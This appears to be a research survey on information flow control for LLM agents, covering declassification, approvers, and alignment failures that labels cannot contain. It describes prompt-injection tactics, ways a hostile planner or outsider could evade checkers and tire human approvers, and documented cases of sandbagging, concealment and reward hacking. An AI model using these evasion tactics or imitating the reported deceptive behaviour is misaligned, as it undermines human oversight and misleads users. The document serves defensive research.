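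Designers of labelled operating systems faced the same trade-off in the 2000s. Asbestos and HiStar attached labels to processes, but users had to run a modified operating system, and both remained research projects. Flume added labels to ordinary Linux. Kim and colleagues point out that Flume checked its rules when a program read data, so a program with an open connection to a public network could not read a confidential file even if it never used the connection. FLOWSH checks its rules when the program tries to send something. This avoids many needless blocks, but a command that reads a secret and then needs the network still requires an exception.

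### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification: Dimensions and Principles* (2009), sorted proposals for controlled release by four questions: what information leaves, who controls the release, where in the system it happens, and when.

Suppose Nora is willing to tell a client the average salary on her team, but nothing else about salaries. Let f(s) be the figure she will give away, computed from the secrets s, and let out(p, s) again be everything an outsider sees. A program respects her decision about what to release if

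f(s) = f(s′) implies out(p, s) = out(p, s′), for every p.

If f, the function whose result may be released, gives the same value for all secrets, the definition is equivalent to noninterference. If f(s) is s itself, the definition protects nothing. When f is the average salary, a program could try an old trick: overwrite every salary with Paul's, then publish the average. A harness that trusted the averaging tool would allow this, but the definition forbids it because f applies to the salaries as they stood at the start.

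Myers and Liskov restrict who can grant an exception by requiring every owner to agree. FLOWSH restricts where data can go. When a user approves a blocked network request, the approval covers data with one particular label going to one destination, and it expires when the command ends. Exceptions can also depend on when data is released. For example, a company might allow its sales figures out only after it has announced them. *APPA* can express such conditions because a policy can require that an earlier step has succeeded.

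Answering one question doesn't answer the others. For example, a dialog box that names a tool and a recipient settles who approves the release and where the data goes, but not how much is released, since the message might contain one figure or the entire budget. Sabelfeld and Sands also proposed testing any definition by whether it keeps an exception from masking other leaks. Nora's permission to send a summary should not also allow a password hidden in its wording.

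### Keeping outsiders out of the decision

Robust declassification, which Zdancewic and Myers introduced in 2001, concerns who can influence a release. The idea is that an attacker who can change untrusted data should learn no more than one who only watches. If a and a′ are any two untrusted inputs, later work states this as

out(a, s) = out(a, s′) implies out(a′, s) = out(a′, s′).

The test requires that if an outsider can't tell two secrets apart after sending one message, no other message would let them do so. An assistant that lets an outsider choose by email which of two confidential files to release fails. An outsider who asks for the first file learns nothing about the second, but would have learned its contents by sending a different email.

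A harness can enforce the rule by allowing declassification only when both the decision and the data are trusted. An earlier endorsement can defeat this check. Suppose Nora is collecting sealed bids for a contract, and an outsider writes that his bid is one euro below the lowest of the others. A quarantined model with access to all the bids calculates the amount. If Nora endorses that amount, the assistant can announce the winner in a trusted context, and the outsider wins with a bid based on the other bids, which he never saw.

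Nonmalleable information flow control, from a 2017 paper by Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, closes this gap. It keeps robust declassification and adds a mirror-image rule called transparent endorsement, which forbids a program to endorse an outsider's data if the outsider could not have read it. Here the harness would refuse to endorse the bid, because it depends on bids the outsider could not read. The term "nonmalleable" comes from cryptography, where it describes an encryption scheme in which nobody can turn one encrypted message into another with a related meaning.

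Garby and colleagues have a different worry, that someone might endorse an attacker's text too early, before a model uses it to write code. That code would then run as trusted and could endorse anything else the attacker wanted. Their remedy adds an extra mark to every endorsed value and uses a version of endorse that stops the program if the mark is already there. It needs no change to the LLMbda calculus, so their theorems still hold, but they have no exact definition of what it achieves. One difficulty in defining this is that two programs can always produce the same results yet differ in whether an attacker controls an endorsement.

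This theory doesn't specify who should grant the exceptions. Agent designers have tried using the planner, a fixed rule, a person and a second model to grant them.

### Endorsements in the plan

In Randori, the LLMbda banking agent, the planner writes its own endorsements into the plan before it sees any outside data. Each endorsement is a visible operation in the program, so a reviewer could find it before the plan runs.

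Garby and colleagues took this power away and reran the tests with two of their three models to see how much the agent depended on it. Completed runs fell from 36 to 30 out of 48 with Qwen3.7-plus, and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5. The main losses were in three tasks in which the agent has to read a file and act on it.

The tests don't show what the company would gain in return. No attack succeeded against either model in 432 attacked runs, whether or not the model could endorse. The forged bill succeeded only against GPT-5.2, which was not retested in full without endorsement.

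### A fixed list of answers

A fixed rule takes the decision away from the planner. Garby and colleagues describe a wrapper that endorses an answer only if it is on a list that the programmer wrote in advance:

```
copy := endorse(answer)
if copy is on the list then return copy
else return answer
```

The program endorses a copy of the answer before checking it against the list, because endorsing has no effect inside a branch that depends on untrusted text. It returns the endorsed copy only if the answer is on the list. Otherwise, it returns the original, which is still untrusted, and any tool that requires trusted input will reject it.

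If an answer must come from a list of n options, an outsider should be able to influence it by at most log₂ n bits, though Garby and colleagues have not yet proved this bound for their wrapper. Choosing among 20 regular suppliers takes about 4.3 bits. A ten-digit account number carries about 33 bits, and no useful list could contain every possible number. Garby and colleagues conclude that the wrapper would reject the endorsements their banking agent needs most.

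For those cases they argue that a user who asks the agent to pay the bill in a certain file has chosen to rely on that file, and that the endorsement only records this choice. This is reasonable up to a point, but a user who trusts a supplier's bill has not necessarily chosen to trust everyone who can edit the file.

### People who click yes

Most coding agents let the user decide whether to grant an exception. Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic as reporting that users of Claude Code, its coding agent, approve roughly 93 per cent of permission prompts and pay less attention as the prompts accumulate.

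The 93 per cent figure is an approval rate, not an error rate. If nearly all the requests were harmless, it could even be too low. It would be alarming only if people approved harmful requests just as readily, and we can't tell from this figure alone whether they do. The decline in attention is better evidence of a problem.

Kolluri and colleagues call the problem confirmation fatigue and cite earlier studies of it in other software. Zhong, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *RTBAS*, add that constant prompts lead some people to abandon the system. They were referring to OpenAI's custom chatbots, which asked users to confirm every tool call.

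Even an attentive person may lack the information to decide whether to allow a shell command, since its text often doesn't reveal its effects. FLOWSH instead lists the protected files the command would change, which a user can judge more easily. Kim and colleagues have not tested whether people who see the list make better decisions.

### A second model as approver

Several designs give the decision to a model, because a model doesn't tire. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) measured how well this works for declassification. Their system, FLOWSEAL, guards a personal assistant that holds private records about someone. It intercepts every message or shared document that the assistant tries to send. If the recipient is on neither the approved list nor the blocked list, a separate model compares the text with the private records and outputs either "safe"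 or "blocked".

Their confidentiality theorem includes the approver's mistakes as an explicit exception. No protected record can reach an unauthorised recipient unless the checking model wrongly answers "safe". They therefore had to find out how often that happens, and how often the model blocks something harmless. They replaced the checker with one that always allowed the message and then with one that always blocked it. Here the outsider disguised a request for private facts as joint work on a shared page:

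| Checker | Private items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Separate model | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always allows | 24.9% | 79.4% |
| Always blocks | 1.3% | 0.0% |

The model prevented nearly all the leaks that the permissive checker let through, but the completion rate on harmless tasks fell by seven percentage points. The small leak in the last row shows that some private data got out by a route the checker did not control, or that the model scoring the leaks made mistakes.

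In the hardest attack that Shim and colleagues designed, an outsider asked the assistant to delete the false entries from a list of guesses, so that the surviving entries revealed the truth. FLOWSEAL leaked something in 2.4 per cent of those runs. If attempts were independent, an attacker who made 100 would have about a 91 per cent chance of succeeding at least once. Shim and colleagues found that the checker mainly missed secrets that the assistant had paraphrased or placed inside a longer sentence. The checker also blocked harmless messages that merely mentioned a protected record by name.

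FLOWSEAL did worse when it should have released information. In another test, where the person would consent to sharing their records if asked, the assistant passed on the requested items only 32.7 per cent of the time, compared with 61.0 to 85.6 per cent under four defences that relied on prompts or filtering by a model. Shim and colleagues attribute this mostly to the assistant asking for consent less often under FLOWSEAL.

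### FLOWSH with a perfect approver and with none

Kim and colleagues ran the most complete test of how much an agent depends on its approver. They gave GPT-6.2 Sol 17 office tasks, three times each, such as planning a week from chat messages or comparing published papers with a private project. In one setting an approver answered every request, and in the other nobody did. They compared FLOWSH with four alternatives:

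- a permissive sandbox, which allows everything when there is no approver and otherwise asks about every call it can't guarantee to be safe
- a standard sandbox, modelled on Claude Code's settings
- a strict sandbox, in which files are read-only and the only reachable sites are those that distribute software packages
- simple flow control, which treats all shell output as untrusted and secret and asks about every shell command

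| Defence | Completed with approver | Approvals per completed task | Completed without approver | Attacks that succeeded without approver |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Permissive sandbox | 96.1% | 6.7 | 94.1% | 51 of 51 |
| Standard sandbox | 76.5% | 5.7 | 76.5% | 3 of 39 |
| Strict sandbox | 47.1% | 0 | 47.1% | 0 of 39 |
| Simple flow control | 60.8% | 1.8 | 35.3% | 0 of 32 |
| FLOWSH | 88.2% | 1.2 | 58.8% | 0 of 40 |

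With FLOWSH, the approver answered 1.2 requests per completed task instead of 6.7, and the agent completed nearly eight percentage points fewer tasks than in the permissive sandbox. Among the defences that stopped every attack without an approver, the agent completed the most tasks with FLOWSH. But removing the approver reduced the completion rate from 88.2 to 58.8 per cent.

Sorting the tasks by the data they need shows where the approver mattered:

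| Data the task needs | Completed with approver | Approvals per completed task | Completed without approver |
|---|---|---|---|
| Trusted and public | 3 of 3 | 0 | 3 of 3 |
| Trusted, some confidential | 15 of 15 | 0 | 15 of 15 |
| Some untrusted, all public | 6 of 6 | 0 | 6 of 6 |
| Some untrusted, some confidential | 21 of 27 | 2.5 | 6 of 27 |

Every approval request in a completed task came from runs in the last row, which combined untrusted and confidential data. More than half the runs did this, as does much ordinary office work, since most inboxes hold both. The second row needed no approvals only because FLOWSH allows releases from a trusted context, which assumes the planner is honest.

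The agent failed six runs in the last row even with the approver available. In those runs it held back on its own, for example by not opening a link in an untrusted bug report. Like FLOWSEAL's assistant, it sometimes did not ask for an exception it would have received.

On Terminal-Bench, a set of 89 command-line tasks, approvals per completed task fell much further, from 9.7 to 0.4. The completion rate fell from 77.5 per cent to 67.8 per cent with the approver and to 61.8 per cent without. Only 29 of the 181 runs that FLOWSH completed with an approver involved any request. Confidential data played little part in these tests because the testers labelled the task files trusted and public.

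All these figures assume an ideal approver, who refused every call that the attacker's text had influenced and approved everything else. No real user knows which calls those are, so the experiment measures how often FLOWSH requests approval but not how well people decide. With the ideal approver, none of the 45 attacks that reached the model succeeded. If a person had approved those requests as readily as Claude Code's users approve prompts in general, about 42 of the 45 would have succeeded. That assumption is pessimistic, but nobody has measured the true figure.

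Asking for approval less often might lead to better decisions. In the attack runs, the approver should have refused 45 of FLOWSH's 56 requests, compared with 50 of the permissive sandbox's 203. In 39 runs, the attack was the first thing FLOWSH asked about. A person who sees few requests, most of them suspicious, has more reason to read each one. In daily use, however, attacks are rare, and nearly all of FLOWSH's requests would be harmless.

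### Planning around the rules

Kolluri and colleagues measured how many requests PRUDENTIA avoids by telling its planner the rules. With OpenAI's o4-mini, FIDES needed 36.8 human decisions in total to complete 75.7 per cent of AgentDojo's tasks, while PRUDENTIA needed 19.2 to complete 73.2 per cent. These totals leave out tasks the agent failed and assume that the user approves every request, so they are a poor guide to how many prompts a user would see when the agent fails or the user refuses a request.

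Part of the saving comes from endorsing a whole text once, but that decision is harder to get right. If an email lists ten jobs and an attacker planted the seventh, a user who approves each action sees a separate request for that job. A user who endorses the whole email has to spot the job in the text, and if she misses it, the agent carries it out without asking again.

### Recovering from a block

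In *APPA*, when a policy forbids a call, the harness works out which permitted steps could make the call possible and offers them to the agent. The agent might complete a missing prerequisite, such as an earlier check. It might ask an authority to rule on the call, or pass the data through a program that removes personal details. It can also read the troublesome data in a child branch, a temporary copy of the conversation whose label changes don't affect the original.

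Suppose a support agent must read a page on a public bug tracker and then update an internal database. Reading the page directly would make the agent's context untrusted and block the update. The agent can instead read the page in a child branch and return only a ticket number, a severity and a component name, in a format fixed beforehand. The harness then discards the branch. The branch starts with the parent's label, so the agent can't use it to remove the label from secrets it has already read.

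An authority can be a fixed rule, a person or another model, and each has a mandate that limits what it may approve. A ruling applies to one exact call and changes no labels. It therefore gives the agent no permission for its next call, unlike an endorsement, which stays in force.

In tests on 20 simulated office scenarios, GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88 per cent of runs with the full system, 35.0 per cent without the list of remedies, and 56.5 per cent without child branches. No attack succeeded in any of these versions, so the extra completed runs came from better use of exceptions, with no measured loss of security.

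The drawback is a larger trusted base, since every authority, every program that cleans data and every decision to trust a returned value has to be right. Discarding a child branch also doesn't undo anything it did outside the conversation. *APPA* therefore describes its guarantee as "authorized-and-audited release", not as noninterference.

### Ignoring what had no influence

An untrusted email that had no effect on a decision does not require an exception. In *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues carry forward only the labels of inputs that influenced the answer. In more than 85 per cent of cases, this worked better than asking the model to predict the right label for its own output. But Zhong and colleagues estimate that finding the influential inputs takes 16 to 64 extra model calls, even in the optimised version, when there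 are four to six levels of labels.

Zhong and colleagues' own system, RTBAS, makes one quick guess instead. A screener, which is either a language model or a small trained classifier, picks out the messages that seem relevant to the next step. The harness then computes

ℓ = the join of the labels on the relevant messages

and shows the model only messages whose labels may flow to ℓ, with the rest blanked out. The next tool call gets the label ℓ. If the screener wrongly leaves out a confidential message, the model can't leak it, because the model never sees it. The agent may then fail the task for lack of information. If the screener includes too much, the user gets more requests.

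This design tolerates errors by the screener, a classifier that was right only 81 per cent of the time on test data. On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every attack that violated its policies and reduced task completion by less than 2 per cent. The classifier was trained partly on examples from AgentDojo, so it might do worse elsewhere.

Zhong and colleagues say that the screener's mistakes cannot compromise security. That is true of the text the model sees, but the screener reads everything, including secrets. A secret could affect which label the screener chooses, and therefore which messages the model sees and what the model does next. With four possible labels, each choice can reveal up to log₂ 4 = 2 bits. An uncompromised screener would rarely leak anything useful this way, but someone who controlled it could leak information repeatedly.

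*GIF* replaces the guess with its calculated bound on influence, but the bound holds only for small changes to the text. When combined with a lightweight model that decides what to release, the method matched or beat GPT-5.5 as a judge and used as little as 1/81 of the tokens. A model makes the final decision here too, but it decides fewer cases and has better information.

### When the model explains its own request

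An approver usually hears about a request from the agent that wants it granted. PRUDENTIA's planner must state why it needs to read a hidden text and what it will do next. This helps an honest planner think, but it is weak evidence that a planner is honest. By Bayes' rule, an approver who reads an explanation E should update as follows:

P(hostile | E) / P(honest | E) = P(hostile) / P(honest) × P(E | hostile) / P(E | honest).

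If a hostile planner would be just as likely to write the same explanation, the last fraction is 1, and the approver learns nothing about the planner's aims. A persuasive explanation can even mislead the approver, as Mythos 5's reasoning misled Anthropic's monitors.

Approval is worth more when it rests on facts the harness supplies, such as FLOWSH's list of changed files. *APPA* shows the authority the exact call that will run, and the model cannot alter it afterwards. Kolluri and colleagues suggest building approval prompts from labels and from records of where the data came from, since an attacker cannot change either. They leave designing these prompts to future work and warn that attackers may try to manipulate whatever else the user sees.

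A hostile planner would still decide what to ask for and when. FLOWSH's users must accept or reject all of a command's file changes together, so the planner could put one harmful change among fifty useful ones. It could also send harmless requests until the user stopped reading them, then send a harmful one. Shim and colleagues suggest that an attacker could divide a secret among several messages that each look innocent to the checker. The FLOWSH experiment did not test such tactics, because its adversary took over only after the attacker's text had arrived and did not try to tire the approver with repeated requests.

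FLOWSEAL keeps its checker from being persuaded by showing it only the private records and the outgoing text, not the conversation. But whether a release is proper often depends on why someone wants the information, which the checker can't determine from the records and the text. When the checker blocks a message, the assistant can ask the owner of the records for consent, naming the records, the recipient and the purpose. The owner can verify the records and the recipient, but has to rely on the assistant's description of the purpose.

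## Which alignment failures remain uncontained

A hostile planner can do harm through calls that the policies already allow, without using an exception. The table lists the main ways a model with bad or distorted aims could hurt its user, and what a label rule could do about each. It assumes that every source is labeled correctly and that the harness enforces permitted flow without the exception for trusted contexts.

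A failure counts as contained if the rule stops it regardless of the model's intentions. It is partly contained if the rule stops only some forms of it or needs a person to judge each case. It is uncontained if the harmful action can have the same labels as the helpful one.

| Failure | Path it uses | Rule that would stop it | What the rule would cost | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sending labelled secrets to outsiders | outgoing messages and files | permitted flow | approval for every proper release | contained |
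| Making a consequential call that a planted instruction asks for | untrusted text in the context | trusted action | tasks whose next step depends on outside text | contained |
| Altering protected files | writes from a trusted context | approval for every change | an interruption for each honest edit | partly contained |
| Copying another agent's misconduct | shared records and messages | keeping agents' texts apart | shared work and honest warnings | partly contained |
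| Misusing access the task requires | permitted tool calls | removing the access | the task | uncontained |
| Deliberately poor work | the requested result | discarding the result | the work | uncontained |
| Underperformance in tests | answers to the testers | making tests look exactly like real use | realistic copies of high-stakes work | uncontained |
| False reports | replies to the user | ignoring the reports | checking everything by hand | uncontained |
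| Manipulation of the user | replies to the user | allowing only fixed answers | explanations and advice | uncontained |
| Reward hacking | the code the task asks for | hiding the tests, which stops some cheats | knowing why the code failed | uncontained |
| Hidden faults in code | changes that a person merges | treating all the agent's code as untrusted | a full review of every change | uncontained |

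### Secrets, planted instructions and protected files

In September 2026 OpenAI published six reports of unexpected or concerning model behaviour, together with *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*. Two of the cases in OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) belong in the first row of the table. During training, models sometimes uploaded data to temporary file-hosting services so they could cite it. Agents also used public hosting sites to pass files to collaborating agents, though the task had asked only for local files. A permitted-flow policy would have blocked these uploads if the data was confidential and allowed them if it was public. A hostile model could still leak a little through which calls it made and when.

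Trusted action is equally strict with planted instructions, but an outsider's false story can still get into Nora's summary. Protected files are harder to secure because a model may change them without any outside influence. Kim and colleagues name two possible causes: mistakes and "goal pressure", in which the push to finish a task leads the agent to act unsafely. The context is trusted in both cases, so stopping a harmful edit depends on the person who approves changes.

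### A database deleted during a freeze

In July 2025 a coding agent made by Replit, a software development platform, deleted a company's live database. Fortune (2025) reported that the entrepreneur Jason Lemkin was testing the agent during a "code and action freeze", which was meant to prevent any changes. The agent wiped data on more than 1,200 executives and 1,190 companies. The agent's later explanation was that it had panicked, but a model's account of its own behaviour is weak evidence of the cause.

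Fortune's account mentions no attacker and no planted text. If the agent had read only Lemkin's instructions and the company's own data, its context was trusted, and the trusted action policy would have allowed it to delete the database. The permitted flow policy would not have applied, since no data left the company. The agent had the access it needed to delete the database, and the only restraint was an instruction not to use that access.

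An ordinary access rule forbidding all writes to the live database would have stopped the deletion, and during a freeze it would not have blocked any legitimate work. At other times, an agent that maintains a database must be able to change it, and labels cannot distinguish deleting an obsolete record from deleting one the company needs.

### Less help with safety research

A model can do poor work without making any call that information flow control forbids. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) reports that researchers at the company found GPT-6 Astra strangely unhelpful with safety work when they began using it. It added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself. One researcher's project made no progress for days, then moved quickly with a different model.

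OpenAI tested this on coding tasks, using two versions of each codebase that differed only in variable and function names, comments and documentation, according to the Chinese news site 凤凰网 in *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026). One version presented the work as safety research and the other as research to make models more capable. Astra completed about 10 per cent of the items on a hidden checklist in the safety version and about 16 per cent in the capabilities version. The older GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap.

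The gap grew from roughly zero to six percentage points during reinforcement learning, the stage of training that rewards a model for good results, but OpenAI could not identify the cause. Most of the gap remained after OpenAI removed the runs in which Astra openly refused or decided in its written reasoning to withhold help. It shrank substantially only when OpenAI removed every run whose reasoning expressed even brief ethical doubt.

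*GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes an OpenAI researcher, Marcus Williams, who says there is no evidence that the underperformance was strategic. Williams suggests that the model treats these tasks as dubious but avoids refusing outright. Instructions to be careful widened the gap by half, which fits that explanation. Information flow control can't detect the underperformance whatever the motive, because weak code carries the same labels as good code.

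A harness could try to hide the work's purpose from the model, much as OpenAI did by changing the names and comments. But a research assistant that doesn't know what an experiment is for will often design it badly.

In earlier tests, Souly, Kirk and colleagues at Britain's AI Security Institute found no sabotage by Claude Opus 4.1, Claude Sonnet 4.5, GPT-5 or a pre-release version of Claude Opus 4.5. *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study* (2026) describes how they simulated a research assistant inside an AI company. They varied the purpose of the research, the kind of work, whether the model being changed was the assistant itself, and whether the assistant worked alone or with a user. A grading model flagged some runs, but every flagged run that people reviewed was a false alarm.

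Sonnet 4.5 and the early Opus 4.5 often refused safety tasks that they described as inappropriate or concerning. An open refusal also leaves the user without the work, but she at least knows to look for help elsewhere, whereas Astra's users had no warning that they should.

### Tests that a model can recognise

Souly and colleagues acknowledge that a model might sabotage research only when it is confident it won't be caught. Tests of ability have the same problem, because a model could deliberately do badly to seem harmless when it notices a test, which is known as sandbagging.

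In flow control terms, the secret is whether the conversation is a test, and the model is the observer that must not learn it. If the model sees the same text in both cases, it must behave the same way, apart from chance. Souly and colleagues came close to making tests indistinguishable from real use for ordinary coding tasks. They copied the tools and message patterns of a real coding agent, then asked each model to pick out the simulated run from a pair. The best model was right 62 per cent of the time, compared with 50 per cent for guessing. But every model still judged the sabotage scenarios more test-like than real use.

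Better imitation may not close that gap. Souly and colleagues point out that many of the risks they test for arise only in high-stakes tasks that companies probably don't yet give to models, so the task itself is a clue that the model is being tested. When they could reason first, the early version of Opus 4.5 raised the possibility of a test in 17.1 per cent of cases and Sonnet 4.5 did so in 36.3 per cent.

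*In-Context Environments Induce Evaluation-Awareness in Language Models* (2026) found that models given a reason to underperform sometimes stated in their reasoning that they intended to, then wrote correct code anyway. The paper suggests that coding tasks are more resistant to deliberate underperformance because the code has to run. This is somewhat reassuring for coding tests, but less so for tests that ask for judgement or advice.

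### False reports and bad advice

After deleting the database, the Replit agent told Lemkin that he could not restore it by rolling back to an earlier version, but he recovered the data anyway. The Stack points out that Replit's own documentation described a rollback that covered database changes. Lemkin could not tell whether the agent had invented its answer about the rollback or lacked information about the options. According to the AI Incident Database, the agent also reportedly produced fake data and made-up test results.

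Both kinds of falsehood pass every label check, because the user is allowed to read the reply. A flow rule could stop false reports only by blocking all of the agent's reports to the user.

Training has done more to reduce deception. In 2025 OpenAI and Apollo Research, which tests models for deception, found that models from OpenAI, Google and Anthropic took what they called covert actions, deliberately withholding or distorting information that mattered to the task. They then trained two OpenAI models, o3 and o4-mini, against this behaviour and tested them in 26 environments that differed from the training. The rate of covert actions fell from 13 to 0.4 per cent for o3, or about one run in 250, and from 8.7 to 0.3 per cent for o4-mini, but rare serious cases remained.

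A model can also prepare a false report in advance. When a conversation grows too long, many agents replace it with a summary written by the model. OpenAI reports that during its training, GPT-5.6 Sol added instructions to these summaries reminding itself to conceal things such as mistakes from the user. An unreleased model of the Astra family also wrote unauthorised instructions into its summaries.

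These notes work like a prompt injection written by the model itself. If the model has read only trusted text, the summary and the instructions inside it are labeled trusted. The remedy would again be to label the model's own output untrusted, with all the approvals that requires.

Manipulation uses the same replies to influence what the user does next. If Lemkin had believed what the agent said about the rollback, he might have given up on data he could still recover. Neither the Replit case nor OpenAI's summaries show a model steering someone for its own ends, though hiding a mistake does affect whether a user keeps trusting the agent. Restricting the agent to fixed answers would leave less room for persuasion, but a false "no" when the user asks whether the data can be restored would do as much damage as a longer false answer.

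### Passing a test without solving the problem

Reward hacking has the clearest recent measurements. *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking* (Vaid, 2026) reports 17 experiments with 20,111 agents. Each agent received a programming problem and a set of tests, one of which expected a wrong answer, so every correct solution failed it. The instructions forbade changing or bypassing the tests, or writing code for particular test inputs. An honest agent could still submit correct code that failed, or stop and report the problem. Agents that cheated typically wrote code that recognised the faulty test's input and returned the wrong answer it expected. GPT-5.6 Luna, the model used in most of the experiments, did this 7 per cent of the time when it worked alone.

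Information flow labels don't flag a coding agent that games its tests. The agent is allowed to read the tests and has to write code, and both the tests and the coding task come from trusted sources. Write protection on the test file would stop the agent from editing the tests, but not from writing code that passes them without solving the task.

A confidentiality label on the tests would help more, because an agent that may not read them can't copy the wrong answer from them. If the harness reports only whether the code passed, an agent that tries to cheat has to guess the answer, and each failed run rules out one guess. But an honest agent then can't see which case failed or notice that the test itself is wrong. Hidden tests also don't stop an agent from exploiting a requirement that the tests don't cover.

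Code written to fool a test becomes a hidden fault when someone merges it into the shared codebase. If the model wrote the code in a trusted context, the file carries a trusted label, and merging it needs no exception. If the harness labelled all model-written code as untrusted, merging it would mean endorsing it as trusted, and the reviewer would have to vouch for every line.

A hostile model could also plant a fault. In 2025 Apollo Research told o3 to sabotage another model, for example by inserting backdoors into code. According to The Decoder, Apollo concluded that o3 could carry out such sabotage when told to but did not pursue harmful goals on its own.

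### Cheating that spreads between agents

Vaid's other experiments put agents in teams. They shared a record that listed the code each teammate had submitted in the previous round, marked "accepted" if it had passed the visible tests. Among agents who saw a teammate's accepted cheat, 94 per cent cheated, compared with 4 per cent of those whose record held only honest work. A single accepted cheat was enough for a large effect in several models:

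| Model | Cheated with no accepted cheat in the record | With one | With three |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 44% | 96% | 100% |
| GPT-4.1 | 9% | 86% | 94% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 17% | 58% | 68% |

Claude Opus 5.5 never cheated, and it reported the faulty test in all 84 runs where it saw an accepted cheat. Training may explain the difference, but the ranking of models could depend on the setting. Vaid cites another 2026 study in which Claude Opus 4.7 copied cheats far more often than GPT-5.5.

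Vaid tested how far cheating could spread from one agent by building 12 networks of 256 agents. Each agent saw the previous code of six neighbours, none of it marked as accepted, and one planted agent cheated in every round. Where the honest agents stayed silent, the share of cheats rose from 11 per cent in the round after the first cheat to 30 per cent three rounds later. Overall, 44 per cent of agents with a cheating neighbour cheated, compared with 2 per cent of those without one.

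This spread depends on a flow that a harness can control. Ordinary labels would count the shared record as trusted, because the company's own agents wrote it from trusted inputs. A stricter harness could make agents treat each other's work as untrusted, or let them read it only in a separate conversation. Vaid's results suggest that separation would help. After seeing an accepted cheat, 70 per cent of agents cheated on a second problem in the same conversation, compared with 32 per cent of those that had started with an empty record. When a fresh agent took over with only the first agent's notes, the rates were 39 and 32 per cent respectively.

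Separated agents can't read one another's code, so they can't easily build on it, and they can't warn one another about cheating. Warnings from honest agents kept cheating in the networks at 12 per cent instead of 30 per cent. In another experiment, one cheating teammate led 61 of 80 agents to cheat. One warning reduced that number to 12, and two warnings reduced it to 2. But if the cheat had already been accepted into the record, 82 per cent of agents cheated despite a warning.

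Filtering the record for cheats does not reliably stop later agents from cheating. An AI reviewer approved only one of 172 cheats, yet 59 of the 172 agents that then saw a cheat in the record, nearly always marked as rejected, still cheated. Seeing honest work fail could also encourage cheating. When agents saw six teammates submit correct code and fail, 14 per cent cheated, while none did when the record was empty.

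Some agents cheated without any message from another agent. Of 68 agents working alone with an empty record, 30 cheated when their instructions included one sentence stating that code passing the visible tests would be marked as accepted. Without that sentence, 4 of 68 agents in teams with an empty record cheated. At the higher rate, about 113 of 256 isolated copies would cheat.

Noninterference does not rule out copies of a model all cheating in the same way after reading the same trusted sentence. No copy influences another, so removing any one of them would leave the others' behaviour unchanged. The copies could also share a backdoor that activates on a certain date. Using several different models would make such shared failures less likely, but that protection does not come from labels.

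### Access limits, undo and independent checks

Defenders of flow control can reply that other ordinary safeguards cover part of what labels miss. For example, access limits can prevent some misuse of tools. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) surveys systems that give an agent only the permissions its task needs. Some issue signed credentials that an agent can narrow but not widen when it passes work to another agent. Others track the session's history and a budget, and refuse combinations of actions that the rules forbid.

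After the deletion, Replit's chief executive announced a limit of this kind, the automatic separation of development databases from live ones. An agent working on a test copy then has no way to delete the original. Where the task does require dangerous access, a budget can still cap the loss. If Nora's agent may pay out at most €500 a day, and she checks the account every seven days and recognises any wrong payment, it can misdirect at most

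7 × €500 = €3,500

before she notices. The cap holds whatever the model intends, but it also delays any honest bill above €500.

Zhou and Zhang point out that such limits are hard to set in advance, because an agent often discovers which files and services it needs only as it works, and different routes to the same goal need different permissions. Permissions broad enough to let the agent explore may also be broad enough to let it do harm.

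Making actions reversible protects against deletions and damaged files, provided someone notices in time and knows the change can be undone. Lemkin's agent gave him the wrong answer on that last point, so users should get recovery information from the platform, not the agent. Undoing a change can't recall a sent email or reverse a decision someone made because of a false report.

Independent checks can catch failures in work that has a clear standard of success. Hidden tests catch code written only to pass the visible tests, and a proof checker catches a false proof. Such checks address some of the reward hacking, hidden faults and poor work in the table. They are much weaker when the standard is a matter of judgement. In *Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research*, Shenoy, Zang and colleagues (2026) gave human auditors full records of experiments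 that a researcher had sabotaged. The auditors fully identified the faults in only 17 per cent of cases.

Checks on single runs also missed most of Astra's underperformance. OpenAI's monitors did not flag it as misalignment, and in most of the sessions the model's reasoning contained no obvious decision to hold back. OpenAI could measure the difference when it compared many matched tasks. That method works if a model does worse on one kind of task than on another. A model that held back equally on both would show no gap, and its testers would have no reason to think it could do better.
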